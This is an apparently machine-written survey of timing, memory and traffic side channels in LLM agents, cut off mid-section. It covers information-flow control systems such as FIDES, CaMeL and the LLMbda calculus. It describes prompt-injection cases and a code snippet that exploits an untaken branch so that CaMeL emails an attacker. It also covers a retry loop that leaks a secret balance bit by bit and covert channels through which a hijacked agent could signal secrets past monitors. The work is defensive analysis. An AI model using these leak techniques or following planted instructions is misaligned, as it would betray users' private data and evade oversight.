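# Timing, memory and traffic side channels in LLM agents, and the limits of constant-time defences

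## Agents, inference engines and who can observe them

A side channel is a property of a computer system, such as its running time or the size of the packets it sends, that unintentionally reveals information about secret data. If an encryption routine runs slightly longer for some keys than for others, an observer who can time it precisely may be able to work out the key. Cryptographic libraries therefore rely on constant-time code, whose branches and memory addresses do not depend on secrets. Large language models (LLMs) create similar side channels for ordinary text. A long answer takes longer to generate than a short one, and a system built around a model may contact three websites for one input and none for another, so an observer can learn something about the text without reading it.

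Agents have the most information to leak. *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks* (Pouryousef, Lopez and colleagues, 2026) defines an LLM agent as software that combines one or more models with tools, memory and workflow logic to plan and carry out tasks on its own. The model acts through tool calls. It writes a structured request, such as "search the mailbox for this sender", and the surrounding software executes it and adds the result to the model's context, the text on which its next output depends. The model then runs again, and this cycle repeats until it returns a final answer.

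An agent can repeat this loop many times for one request. *TraceLab* (Zhu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) reports an average of 8.8 model calls and 10.8 tool calls per user request in logs from 43 developers who used the coding agents Claude Code and Codex. A minority of requests with many calls raise these averages, and the median request needed two tool calls. *Understanding KV Residency in Production-Scale Agentic LLM Workloads* (Arya, Bari and colleagues, 2026) reports 9.38 model calls per user turn for a research agent in Microsoft's production traces, compared with 2.49 for an enterprise chat product.

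Some of what an agent reads comes from strangers, and models cannot reliably separate data from instructions. Prompt injection exploits this by putting instructions in data the agent reads, which the model then follows. In an example from *AttriGuard* (2026), an email tells an assistant to forward the user's passport number to an outside address. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) credits Greshake and colleagues with demonstrating the attack in 2023. It describes the underlying fault as a mismatch of authority, since the email's sender has no right to direct the assistant. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (2026) points out that injected text can do more than bias a web agent's answer, because the agent also navigates pages and selects tools.

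A filter on outgoing messages might well catch a passport number, but it would miss an agent that leaks information about the number by waiting two seconds instead of one before its next web request. Noninterference means that changing the secret inputs does not change what an observer sees, so whether a security system provides it depends on what the observer can measure.

### One task, step by step

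Suppose a user asks an agent to deal with an email about an insurance claim. The agent reads the email, looks up the user's private claim record, calls a web tool to check the insurer's current rules, and writes an answer. This takes four model calls and three tool calls if nothing goes wrong.

| Step | What it exposes besides its text |
|---|---|
| Read the email | Start and end time of the mailbox query; size of the reply; growth of the context, and so of memory use in every later model call |
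| Look up the record | Whether the lookup happened at all; how long the database took; how much data came back |
| Call the web tool | The destination; the sizes and directions of packets; the moment the request arrives |
| Answer | The time and size of each piece of the reply; the total duration |

The number and order of the calls also reveal information. If the agent consults the web only for claims above a certain value, anyone who observes a web request can infer that the claim in the private record is above that value.

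Two studies of real traffic show this structure clearly, even though encryption hid the content. In *ANT*, Li, Gao and colleagues (2026) recorded Claude Code answering a question and matched its model calls and tool events to the network flows of the same period. Traffic came in bursts near the start of each stage. During a web search, nearly all of it went to the model's own servers, because Claude Code delegates searching to them, whereas fetching a specific page added address lookups and a download from the site. In *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025) found similar patterns on the link between user and agent. A search produced one burst for retrieval and another for the summary, drawing a diagram through a slow outside service left a long idle gap, and plain conversation gave a fairly even flow.

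### How an engine turns text into time

A language model works on tokens, which are words or pieces of words. The inference engine, the program that runs the model, handles a request in two phases. In prefill it processes the whole prompt, many tokens in parallel. In decode it produces output tokens one at a time, and each new token depends on all the earlier ones. Most services stream the reply, sending tokens to the client as the engine produces them.

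To avoid repeating work, the engine stores intermediate results, called keys and values, for every token so far at each layer. This store is the KV cache. Arya and colleagues could not disclose the models behind their traces, so they estimated the cache's size from the published layout of Llama-2-70B. That model has 80 layers with 8 key-value heads each, and every head stores a key and a value of 128 numbers per token. At 2 bytes per number, each token takes 327,680 bytes. In the research agent's sessions, the median context grew from about 10,000 tokens to 68,000 by the thirtieth model call. Memory use grows in proportion to the amount of text, so on that layout it would rise from 3.3 to 22 gigabytes.

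Two measures describe the timing that a client sees. Bhimani, Escobar and colleagues (2026), in *Benchmarking LLM Inference on Desktop-Scale NVIDIA Grace Blackwell Clusters*, define time to first token (TTFT) as the delay between submitting a request and receiving the first output token, and inter-token latency (ITL) as the mean gap between consecutive output tokens. TTFT mostly reflects waiting in the queue plus prefill; ITL reflects the pace of decoding. For a reply of $N$ tokens, Yan and Zhang (2026), in *Mirage*, write the total latency as

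$$\text{TTFT} + \sum_{i=2}^{N} \text{ITL}_i .$$

The coding-agent logs supply realistic values. For Codex, Zhu and colleagues estimated a TTFT of 3.1 seconds and a median decode speed of 61.3 tokens per second, or an ITL of about 16 milliseconds. The median output across both agents was 214 tokens. Put together, a typical model call looks like this:

| Time | Event |
|---|---|
| 0 s | The client sends the request |
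| 3.100 s | The first token arrives (TTFT = 3.1 s) |
| 3.116 s | The second token arrives (ITL = 16 ms) |
| about 6.6 s | Token 214, the last, arrives |

If the reply had been half as long, it would have ended at about 4.8 seconds. An observer who knows the usual TTFT and ITL can therefore estimate a reply's length from its duration. The estimate from a single call is rough, because speeds in these logs varied a lot from call to call.

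Agents send long prompts and get short outputs. *Validation-driven Deployment of LLM Inference Platforms for Agentic Workloads* (2026) covers a production deployment in which the median request had 50,000 to 100,000 input tokens and 200 to 500 output tokens. To avoid prefilling the whole prompt again at each step, engines use prefix caching. When a new prompt begins with text the engine has already processed, the engine reuses the stored KV entries and prefills only the rest. A cache hit shortens TTFT, and where users share one cache, the difference in TTFT can reveal other users' text.

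Users also affect one another through the schedule. An engine does not finish one request before starting the next. It works in steps, and Ramani and Tantawi (2026), in *An Approximate Queueing Model of LLM Inference Serving for SLO-Driven Autoscaling*, explain how requests join and leave the running batch at every step boundary, a design whose usual name is continuous batching. They model the duration of a step with $X$ active requests as

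$$T(X) = \alpha + X\delta ,$$

where $\alpha$ is a fixed overhead and $\delta$ is the average work that each request adds. The formula is simple, but the model built on it predicted average ITL with a relative error of about 5% for one model and 8% for another, at light to moderate load. So when a stranger's request joins the batch, everybody's next token comes a little later. Long prompts have a stronger effect. The open-source engine vLLM cuts them into chunks and schedules the chunks alongside other requests' decoding. In Bhimani and colleagues' set-up the limit was 2,048 tokens per step, so that a prompt of 8,192 tokens occupied at least four steps.

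### Accidental leaks and deliberate signals

Concern about programs that leak data through their side effects long predates language models. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, imagined a customer who gives private data to a service program written by someone else. The confinement problem is how to stop that program from passing the data to anyone except its caller. Lampson listed ways the program could leak the data, such as writing it to a file that the program's owner can read later or encoding a few bits in the bill for the service. The last and subtlest way was for the service to vary its ratio of computing to input and output, or its paging rate (how often it moves memory to and from disk). This changes the performance of the whole machine, and another program running at the same time can measure the change. The channel is noisy, but Lampson observed that suitable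 coding would get the message through, though perhaps very slowly, as long as the effect was not zero.

In Lampson's terms, the user is the customer, the agent is the service, and whoever wrote the document the agent has just read acts as the service's owner. The agent can therefore start working against the user in the middle of a task. Lampson's surest remedy, forbidding a confined program to call any other program, was impractical in 1973 and would leave an agent without tools. For customers willing to accept some leakage, Lampson also suggested a less strict remedy, which is to limit the channel's capacity, or how much information it can carry.

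A covert channel now means a side effect that a sender deliberately varies to pass information where communication is forbidden. In a side channel, the victim leaks information by accident, though the physical signal can be identical. Song, Cao and colleagues (2026), in *A Footprint-Sensitive Cross-GPU Timing Channel Through the Shared Host Memory Subsystem*, built both kinds of channel on the same measurement. Their attacker runs on one graphics processor (GPU) and repeatedly times reads of its own buffer in the host computer's main memory. When a program on a second GPU writes to many different pages of that memory, the two compete for the same memory controller and the attacker's reads slow down. With a cooperating sender that alternated bursts of writing and silence, the channel carried 20 bits per second almost without error, enough to send a 128-bit key in under seven seconds. When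 a language model replaced the sender, the duration of the slowdown tracked the length of each reply with a rank correlation of 0.99.

The passive attack was the more fragile of the two. It failed on about a third of freshly started victim processes, and a production serving stack whose transfers came in bursts stayed below the threshold for leakage. This is roughly as expected, because a passive listener, unlike a deliberate sender, cannot choose a signal that is easy to read.

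Not every author uses intent to distinguish covert channels from side channels. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) applies Lampson's problem to agents but reserves "covert channel" for data hidden inside a message. It classes timing, size and message counts as side channels even when a compromised agent manipulates them on purpose. Under the more common definition, such deliberate manipulation is also a covert channel.

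Covert channels also differ in how the receiver reads them. *Exploiting Page Faults for Covert Communication* (2025) sets out the usual division between storage and timing channels. In a storage channel, the sender changes some stored state, such as a file's size or permissions, and the receiver looks it up. In a timing channel, the receiver measures how long something takes. Allocation channels are similar to storage channels, but the signal is how much of a shared resource the sender occupies. On the Llama-2-70B layout, an agent that reads 10,000 extra tokens uses another 3.3 gigabytes of KV cache, and an observer with access to memory statistics could notice this without a clock. The categories can overlap, as with a prefix cache entry, which is stored state but which another user of the engine can detect only by timing a request.

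*AgenticOS* (2026), a proposal for a secure operating system, lists four channels that remain open to agents even after the system forbids raw data streams: the interval between calls, the length of otherwise legitimate outputs, whether the agent calls an interface at all, and the choice among several acceptable wordings, which is the only one of the four that lies in the text itself.

### Four observers

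How much any of this matters depends on who is measuring, and from where.

A network eavesdropper sits on the path between the machines, for instance at an internet provider or on the same local network. Pouryousef and colleagues represent everything this observer sees as a list of triples $(t_i, s_i, d_i)$, giving the time, size and direction of each packet. In their model, the observer cannot see network addresses. A real capture usually includes them, and Li and colleagues list destinations among the visible features. Work that stays inside one machine, such as a query to a local database, appears only as a gap in the traffic.

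Another tenant, meaning a customer whose requests run on the same engine, cannot see the victim's packets. In Yan and Zhang's threat model, this attacker is an ordinary client who can open several accounts, send chosen prompts and flood the cache, but can observe only the timing of replies to those prompts. The tenant can learn about other users only through a shared cache or schedule.

A process on the same machine, such as Song and colleagues' attacker, can observe the computation much more closely. *Detokenization Leaks* (Weiss, Konstantinov and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack on models that people run on their own computers. The model emits each token as a number, and the processor converts it to text through a lookup table, so different tokens touch different memory addresses. An unprivileged program on the same processor core can fill the core's cache with its own data, then time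 its own accesses to find out which of that data the victim displaced. The researchers used this attack to recover the approximate meaning of outputs, including those of OpenClaw, a popular locally hosted agent.

The operator of a tool or website that the agent contacts can read everything the agent sends to the site and see when each action comes. Lugoloobi, Marro and colleagues (2026), in *Known By Their Actions*, put a small tracking script on web pages and identified which of 14 models was driving a browser agent from the sequence and timing of its clicks, scrolls and keypresses, with F1 scores (a measure combining precision and recall) of up to 96%. The classifier's performance fell to near chance when the software around the model changed. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) likewise attributes request timing more to the design of the agent system than to the type of agent. The operator does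 not see the model's other output, its traffic with other services or its memory. But an operator who has planted a prompt injection on the page can both instruct the agent to use a covert channel and receive the signal it sends.

Results and defences for one of these observers do not carry over to the others. Yan and Zhang's system delays the stream of tokens so that a cache hit looks like a miss to another client of the engine. They exclude token counts and hardware channels from its scope, and the delay would not protect against a program that monitors the processor's cache while the tokens are converted to text.

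## What information-flow control guarantees and what it leaves out

Information-flow control (IFC) protects an agent's data without relying on the model to recognise an attack. Ordinary access control decides whether an agent may open a file. IFC also governs where the contents may go afterwards, because permission to read a document need not include permission to send it on (Zhou and Zhang, 2026, *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*). The software around the model labels each piece of data, updates the labels as the agent combines data, and checks them before a tool runs.

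### Labels, propagation and checks

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) sets out the simplest scheme, in which a label has two parts. The integrity part marks data as trusted (T) or untrusted (U), and the confidentiality part marks it as public (L, for low) or secret (H, for high). The symbol $\sqsubseteq$ means "may flow to", and the scheme has $T \sqsubseteq U$ and $L \sqsubseteq H$. Trusted data may therefore go into an untrusted document, and public data may go to places cleared for secrets. Untrusted data may not steer an action that requires trust, and secrets may not go to public places. When the agent combines two values, the result takes the more restrictive label in each part. In the insurance task, the email is untrusted and the claim record is secret, so a summary of both is untrusted and secret.

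Labels can also name people. In an example from Microsoft's *information flow control moving toward secure autonomous agents*, an agent reads one email that Alex and Priya may see and another that Alex and Marco may see. A summary of both gets only the readers they have in common:

$$\{\text{Alex}, \text{Priya}\} \cap \{\text{Alex}, \text{Marco}\} = \{\text{Alex}\}.$$

The agent therefore may not send Marco the summary on its own. If Priya had copied Marco in, the set would be {Alex, Marco} and the agent could send it.

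FIDES, a system that Costa and colleagues described in 2025, checks information flow at each tool call. It keeps one label for everything the planning model has read so far. Girrens and Wang (2026) explain in *SPA* that FIDES compares each proposed call with that label and with the labels of the call's arguments, and blocks the call if it would break the tool's policy. Microsoft (2026) now ships FIDES as an experimental feature of its Agent Framework, and demonstrates it with an agent that must read strangers' bug reports on GitHub without giving those strangers access to its tools for writing files and posting comments.

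In an ordinary agent loop, such checks soon block nearly everything useful. Once the agent reads one email from a stranger, the whole conversation counts as untrusted, and every later action that needs trusted input fails. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) gives the example of an email tool that requires a trusted subject and body. A plain tool-calling agent that had read an untrusted message could never use this tool.

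### A planner that never reads the email

The usual way round this is the dual-LLM pattern, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model plans the task and issues tool calls but never reads untrusted data. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads the untrusted data and returns values.

In the insurance task, the privileged model would see only the user's request. From that, it could plan to fetch the email, have the quarantined model extract the claim number, look up the record with that number, and draft an answer. A malicious email could still make the quarantined model return the wrong claim number, but it could not add a step that forwards the record to a stranger.

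CaMeL, by Debenedetti and colleagues, builds on this pattern. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, describe how the privileged model writes its plan as a program in a restricted form of Python, which an interpreter then runs. Each value carries "capabilities", a record of where it came from and who may receive it. Each tool has its own policy function, which checks these capabilities before the tool is called. Girrens and Wang note that these policies can express rules that a simple ordering of labels cannot. However, security then depends on every policy being correct.

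FIDES also hides tool results behind variables to keep untrusted text away from the planner, and lets a quarantined model answer questions about those results in a fixed format. Garby and colleagues point to two places where its designers deliberately relaxed the confidentiality rules. FIDES does not track a secret that influences only which branch a program takes. It can also let through values from a small set, such as yes or no, on the grounds that they carry little information. A choice among eight categories, for example, carries at most three bits. This option was switched off in FIDES's own evaluation. Both decisions are defensible, but on any given run it is hard to tell a harmless release from a leak.

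### What noninterference says

The guarantee that IFC aims at is noninterference. Suppose a program $P$ takes a public input $l$ and a secret input $h$, and let $\text{Obs}$ stand for whatever the observer sees of a run. For a program without randomness, noninterference requires that for every $l$ and every pair of secrets $h$ and $h'$,

$$\text{Obs}(P(l,h)) = \text{Obs}(P(l,h')).$$

Two runs with the same public input must look the same to an observer, even if their secrets differ. The formula also covers integrity if $h$ stands for untrusted input and $\text{Obs}$ for the outputs the system marks as trusted. In that case, an attacker who rewrites the email cannot change any trusted output.

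Language models sample their replies at random, so two runs can differ even with identical inputs. The probabilistic form therefore compares how likely each observation is. For every possible observation $o$, it requires

$$\Pr[\text{Obs} = o \mid l, h] = \Pr[\text{Obs} = o \mid l, h'].$$

Some runs never produce a result, because they loop forever or the monitor stops them. Most practical systems settle for a weaker, termination-insensitive guarantee. For deterministic programs, this guarantee requires the observations to match only when both runs finish, so a secret may affect whether the program finishes but nothing else.

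Combining this with randomness takes some care. Garby and colleagues first tried comparing the probabilities among finished runs only, and found that this gave the wrong definition. The one they adopted works as follows. Let $\mu(o)$ and $\nu(o)$ be the probabilities of finishing with observation $o$ under the two secrets. Each set of probabilities may sum to less than 1, and the shortfall is the chance of never finishing. The two are compatible if some third set $\omega$ satisfies

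$$\mu(o) \le \omega(o), \qquad \nu(o) \le \omega(o), \qquad \sum_o \omega(o) \le 1.$$

In other words, both could be the same distribution with different parts lost to runs that never ended. Suppose an agent answers either "approve" or "refer":

| | Approve | Refer | No result |
|---|---|---|---|
| First secret | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| Second secret | 0.6 | 0.2 | 0.2 |
| Smallest possible $\omega$ | 0.6 | 0.3 | |

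The bottom row sums to 0.9, so the two distributions are compatible. If the first secret gave "approve" with probability 0.9 and "refer" with 0.1, and the second gave the reverse, the bottom row would sum to 1.8 and the program would fail the test. The definition also limits how much can leak. The statistical distance between the two distributions, which is half the sum of the absolute differences, can be at most the average chance of not finishing. In the table, the distance is 0.1 and the limit is 0.2. If a program always finishes, the limit is zero, so the two distributions must be exactly equal.

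### The same text after 2 seconds or 9

All of these definitions depend on $\text{Obs}$, and whoever states the theorem chooses it. Most choose the text.

Suppose the insurance agent requests a claim form from the insurer's website. The quarantined model then summarises the user's private claim record, and only the user may see the summary. Finally, the agent sends the insurer a fixed acknowledgement, "Form received". Assume the first token takes one second and the model then produces 50 tokens per second. The summary is about 50 tokens long for an ordinary record and about 400 for one that mentions a legal dispute.

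| | No dispute | Dispute |
|---|---|---|
| Summary, labelled secret | 50 tokens | 400 tokens |
| Text the insurer receives | "Form received" | "Form received" |
| Delay between the form request and the acknowledgement | about 2 s | about 9 s |

Every label here is correct. The summary stays secret, the acknowledgement contains nothing from the record, and the plan sends it in either case. If $\text{Obs}$ is the text that reaches the insurer, the two runs give equal observations and the program satisfies noninterference. If $\text{Obs}$ is the pair (text, delay), the same program fails, because ("Form received", 2 s) differs from ("Form received", 9 s). An insurer who took any delay above five seconds to mean a dispute would be right nearly every time, unless network and server delays varied by several seconds. If disputed and undisputed claims are equally common, the delay reveals one bit,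 which is all the information there is about whether a dispute exists.

### The LLMbda calculus

The strongest theorem of this kind for agents comes from Garby and colleagues. Their LLMbda calculus is a small programming language that extends the lambda calculus with operations to send a prompt, receive a reply, copy a conversation and clear it. Every value carries a label, and every step of execution updates the labels. The theorem is that every program in the language satisfies termination-insensitive, probabilistic noninterference, including programs that ask a model to write code and then run that code.

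Earlier guarantees were narrower. FIDES has a noninterference theorem for one fixed agent loop, and CaMeL has no comparable theorem. A second LLMbda result shows that secrets stay protected even when an attacker chooses all the untrusted inputs and the program deliberately relabels some of them as trusted (endorsement). The researchers checked their proofs in Lean, a proof assistant. The theorems describe the actual interpreter that calls the model, which avoids a common weakness of formal verification, where the proof covers only a simplified version of the software that users run.

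The theorem does not cover time. An observer sees the final conversation and the final value, as far as the labels allow, and neither records how long the run took. The proof compares each program with an altered version that abandons a computation as soon as its label becomes secret and puts an empty value in its place. The altered version behaves identically for both secrets, and its probabilities are at least as high as those of either real run, so it supplies the $\omega$ that the definition needs. In the insurance example, one empty value would replace the whole summary, whether it was 50 tokens long or 400. The interpreter does have a step budget, called fuel, but the theorem linking the interpreter to the calculus requires only that some budget be large enough, so it does not distinguish a run of a thousand steps from a run of a million.

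To test whether the language was usable, they wrote an agent in it called Randori and ran it on the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a standard benchmark for prompt injection. They ran 16 tasks with nine attacks on each, three repetitions and three models, and the agent resisted all but two of the 1,296 attacks. Such security often makes an agent much less useful. When not under attack, CaMeL with GPT-5.2 completed 67% of the banking tasks with its policy checks off and 38% with them on. Randori completed 75% with its checks always on, which is within sampling error of CaMeL's score with checks off. Girrens and Wang saw a similar fall in their system, from 53% to 29% across AgentDojo, when they turned on information-flow control.

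Endorsement explains part of Randori's advantage. Before seeing any outside data, the planner can decide to treat a particular untrusted value as trusted. Both successful attacks exploited this. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its payment instructions, and the attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. Without endorsement, the agent blocked the attack but also completed fewer legitimate tasks.

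AgentDojo counts an attack as successful when the agent carries out the injected task. In 97 of the 144 pairings of task and attack, the plan would never contain the tool calls the attacker needed, so the dual-model design was generally enough on its own. These scores don't measure timing leaks, so an agent could score perfectly and still have delays that depend on the user's bank balance.

### Two leaks in CaMeL

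Garby and colleagues also found two leaks in CaMeL's handling of secrets, neither of which requires a clock.

The first comes from a branch that the program does not take. CaMeL would block a program that emails an attacker directly if the account balance exceeds a threshold, because the decision to send depends on a secret. The program can take a detour, however, using a trick that Fenton described in 1974. In outline:

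```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email(attacker, "rich")
```

When a branch depends on secret data, CaMeL raises the labels of the variables changed on the path taken, but not of those that would have changed only on the other path.

| | Balance above threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
| `tmp` after the third line | False, secret | True, still public |
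| Fourth line | Skipped, so `rich` keeps its public label | Sets `rich` to False under a public condition |
| `rich` at the end | True, public | False, public |
| Email | Sent | Not sent |

By the last line, `rich` holds the answer to the secret question and is labelled public in both cases, so the policy check allows the email.

The LLMbda calculus avoids the equivalent problem in conversations by stopping a program when a decision based on a secret is about to alter a public conversation. Stopping is visible, so a run can still reveal up to one bit. Termination-insensitive noninterference allows this leak.

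The second leak can reveal more than one bit per run. CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failed attempt and doesn't track labels. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret. If the loop can react to each failure, the first attempt can test whether the balance is above 32,767, each later attempt can halve the remaining range, and 16 attempts are enough to find any balance from 0 to 65,535. CaMeL censors the error messages passed between attempts, but without a formal guarantee. Randori instead retries on mock data and accesses the real account only after settling on a plan.

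Termination is closely related to timing, because an observer can see only that a program has not finished yet, not that it never will. An observer who gives up after a minute has in effect made a crude timing measurement, and can make another if the system reruns the task.

### Leaving the clock out on purpose

Some designs state the omission openly. Jiang, Bai and colleagues (2026), in *PerMIT*, protect an agent's long-term memory against planted content. The planning model sees untrusted memories only as opaque references until a user, or a model standing in for the user, approves the exact text. One of their theorems compares two runs, $\rho_1$ and $\rho_2$, that start alike but whose untrusted content may differ in any way:

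$$\text{DT}(\rho_1) = \text{DT}(\rho_2) \implies \text{Beh}(\rho_1) = \text{Beh}(\rho_2).$$

Here $\text{DT}$ is the full record of what the system displayed for approval and what the reviewer decided, and $\text{Beh}$ is the agent's sequence of operations, tool calls and replies. If the displays and decisions match, hidden content has not influenced that behaviour in any other way. The single-user version has been checked in Lean.

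Jiang and colleagues place timing and termination outside the theorem's scope. The agent cannot exploit time through the memory interface, which returns no clock value or step count. If the agent consults a clock through a tool, the reading counts as untrusted data and stays behind an opaque reference. The theorem does not cover delay that an outside party measures. It also compares runs only over the same number of steps, so it does not account for one run lasting longer than another.

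They are much stricter about other side effects. The agent would learn from an error message about full storage how much text an attacker had planted, so they require the system to delete old untrusted entries silently. When a reviewer goes through several pages of items, the agent receives one overall decision, because an answer for each page would reveal the number of pages. Girrens and Wang exclude side channels beneath the components their design must trust. Tallam and Miller warn that CaMeL does not by itself block leaks through loop counts, errors or timing.

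One argument for such exclusions is that the proofs would otherwise be infeasible. According to *Proving the Absence of Microarchitectural Timing Channels* (2023), timing channels are harder to reason about than storage channels because small variations in execution time are so hard to analyse or prevent. *Time Protection* (2018) credits a proof about seL4, a small operating-system kernel, with eliminating storage channels, but held that no existing formal method could do the same for timing in a non-trivial system. By 2023, researchers were attempting such proofs for processor hardware. Proofs about an agent's timing would be harder still, because its speed also depends on the inference engine and on how many other users' requests share the current batch. A theorem about delays would need a model of both, whereas a theorem about text holds on any machine.

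It also makes sense to close the larger leak first. One unchecked email can contain the whole claim record, whereas the difference between 2 and 9 seconds reveals one bit. Padding every reply to nine seconds would achieve very little if CaMeL's untaken-branch leak were left open.

The history of cryptography is evidence against this. *Specification and Verification of Side Channel Declassification* (2009) recounts that much of the research after Lampson treated covert channels as not worth the effort. Kocher then showed that timing measurements could expose secret RSA keys, and Brumley and Boneh mounted a timing attack on a widely used encryption library across a network. These attacks worked even though the mathematics of RSA was sound, because they measured something the security argument had left out.

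Agents may be more exposed than those libraries were because, unlike an encryption routine, an agent can be made to cooperate with its attacker through a successful prompt injection. *Time Protection* treats a cooperating sender as the worst case for how much a channel can carry. Small leaks also add up over repeated model calls. Zhu and colleagues found that coding agents average 8.8 calls per request, so a channel that leaked one noise-free bit per call would reveal a 128-bit key in about 15 requests. Real channels are noisier and would take more requests, but a channel should not be dismissed just because it leaks only one bit per observation.

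Tractability is a good reason to prove theorems about text first, but it gives users no reason to assume that "noninterference" covers the delay. It would not be hard to define $\text{Obs}$ to include the delay, but the resulting theorem would exclude the insurance agent above and most other agents that let a model process a secret before contacting anyone outside, unless something else hid the difference in how long the model took.

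## How a document could signal through timing and traffic

In the insurance example, the delay revealed a dispute only because records that mention one happen to need longer summaries. A stranger who can get the model to read their text might be able to choose which fact the delay depends on, which would turn an accidental side channel into a covert channel.

The argument that this could happen has four premises:

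1. The document influences a model call.
2. The same call has access to a secret.
3. The document can make the amount of work in that call depend on the secret.
4. Someone outside can measure the amount of work, for example from the delay before the agent's next web request.

A defender needs to break only one of these, but has to break it for every call the agent makes.

Influence is the easiest to establish. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) built an assistant that automatically previews any web page the user mentions. They planted instructions in parts of the page that people rarely see, such as its description for search engines. The user asked only for a summary, but the assistant sent private data to an outside server in about 89% of 480 runs, and 95% of the successful attacks got past safety checks that covered only the final answer. The model was small, the secret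 was in plain view in its context, and there was no information-flow control, so a well-defended agent would probably do much better. Even so, a model could still follow planted text, because information-flow labels only limit what the agent can do afterwards.

### Which designs break which premise

| Design | What it breaks | Where the problem survives |
|---|---|---|
| An ordinary program, with no model, extracts fields from the document | The document's influence | Documents that a fixed program cannot parse |
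| The planner never reads the document (the dual-LLM pattern, CaMeL) | Influence over the plan | The quarantined model still reads it |
| Each source gets its own model call | Access to the secret | Tasks that compare the document with the secret |
| The quarantined model must answer in a fixed format | Most of the variation in answer length | Any free reasoning before the answer |
| The agent finishes all outside contact before it opens the secret | Measurement by a website | Observers on the same network or hardware |

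Separate calls are the cleanest of these measures, because no planted text can make a call depend on data the call doesn't have. The LLMbda calculus makes this easy to express, since a program can clear the conversation before each call. But one call can still influence another through its output. If a quarantined model reads the email and returns free text, and the plan passes that text to a second model along with the claim record, the text may carry planted instructions. The risk is much smaller if the first model can return only a claim number in a fixed format, which could hardly carry instructions.

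The order of steps matters too. If the insurance agent had sent its acknowledgement before opening the record, the insurer would have learned nothing from the delay. Many tasks don't allow this order, because the agent has to alternate between private data and outside tools, using what it finds in one to decide what to ask of the other.

### A model with no tools that still takes time

The hard case is when a quarantined model has to read the document and the secret together. Suppose the user asks whether the figures in the insurer's email match the claim record. The plan passes both to a quarantined model, which may answer only yes or no. The plan then sends the insurer a fixed acknowledgement.

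Planted text in the email cannot add a step to this plan. The model's answer is correctly labelled secret and untrusted, and it never leaves the system. But an interpreter that runs the plan line by line must wait for the answer before continuing. If the planted text gets the model to reason at length whenever the claim exceeds some amount, the acknowledgement goes out later for large claims. The answer can be "yes" for large and small claims alike, so checking the model's output would not reveal the problem.

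FIDES, the system described in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa et al., 2025), narrows this channel by using constrained decoding, which limits the model to tokens that fit a fixed answer format. If the constraint covers everything the model generates, a yes-or-no answer is a token or two long whatever the secret, so planted text can do little to vary the output's length. But if the model may reason freely first, the constraint fixes only the last few tokens of what could be thousands.

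There is good evidence that a model's running time reflects what it has read, even when nobody has planted text in the input. *Time Will Tell* (2024) found a strong correlation between execution time, the number of output tokens and sensitive attributes of the input. An attacker could use these signals to work out the target language of a translation or the result of a classification. However, different inputs led to different outputs in those tasks, so they don't cover the hard case, in which the output stays the same.

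*PolicySniff* (Fu, Shao and colleagues, 2026) came closer to it. An agent ran with one of two hidden settings, which determined whether it should ask for approval before acting. The attacker ran a second program on the same GPU, which timed only its own work and had no access to the agent's prompts or replies. Although the agent processed the same task under both settings, the attacker identified the setting with a balanced accuracy of 94.17% (the average of its accuracies on the two settings). In a broader test, accuracy was still 88.82% on tasks for which both settings led to the same decision.

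The attacker knew the task, had measured both settings in advance, and shared the GPU only with the victim. Its probing tripled the agent's median response time, from 2.5 to 7.5 seconds, which an operator might well notice. An insurer connecting over the internet would have none of the attacker's advantages, but a document written to widen the difference in running time would partly make up for this.

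### Leaks from the plan itself

Some of an agent's work happens outside any model. CaMeL's plan, for example, is a program, and Tallam and Miller describe three ways running it could leak a secret. They reason from CaMeL's design and report no measurements.

The simplest channel is a loop whose number of repetitions depends on a secret. If each repetition fetches a harmless web page, the secret appears in the site's access log as the number of requests. This channel is noiseless for the site's operator, so one run reveals all eight bits of a secret number between 0 and 255. An exception leaks less, because if the program fails only when the secret meets some condition, whether an error occurs reveals one bit per run. Running time can also leak information, as when a program sleeps for a secret number of seconds or when its branches use different parts of the processor's cache.

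An attacker cannot use an email to add such a loop to a CaMeL plan, because the planner never reads the email. But a user's ordinary request can still produce one. If a user asks the agent to check the repair shop's website for each open claim, the shop can count the claims from the requests to its website.

A leak of one bit per run is serious if the attacker can get many runs, and the CaMeL retry loop that Garby and colleagues criticised can provide them. Each retry also gives a timing attacker another chance to measure a delay. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to several cooperating agents, repeats the criticism of the retry loop. It also warns that the classical remedies, listing the covert channels and reducing their capacity, may not be enough as agents become more strategic and communicate in more complex ways.

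### Four channels at the boundary

*AgenticOS* approaches the problem from the agent's contact with the outside world. Its threat model allows an attacker to take over the agent process completely, and it asks what could still get out through interfaces that accept only structured, approved requests. The insurance agent could use the four channels on its list as follows:

| Channel | How the agent could signal a large claim | Who could read it |
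|---|---|---|
| Timing | Wait five seconds instead of three before the next request | The website, or an eavesdropper |
| Size | Send a longer search query than necessary | The website, or an eavesdropper |
| Presence | Look up the insurer's rules, or skip the lookup | The website, or an eavesdropper |
| Content selection | Write "Form received" or "We have received the form" | Whoever can read the message |

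Presence carries one bit per opportunity. Size carries three bits if the observer can tell eight lengths apart. Content selection can carry more than it seems to, because the choice need not involve words. Metere lists field order in a structured message as a possible carrier, and five fields can appear in 120 orders, which is almost seven bits. *AgenticOS* reports no measured rates but accepts that no system can close these channels completely. Metere agrees, arguing that an agent can always leak one bit by choosing whether to send a message.

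Labels already handle part of the list. If the wording, length or existence of a message to the insurer depends on the claim record, a sound IFC system will label the message secret and block it. But an eavesdropper can still measure the size of an encrypted reply that the user is allowed to receive, and the timing of a permitted message can still leak information, as in the insurance example.

### Text that slows a model down

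Someone who wants to signal through that moment must be able to control it from inside a document. The most practical method so far comes from research on increasing other people's bills.

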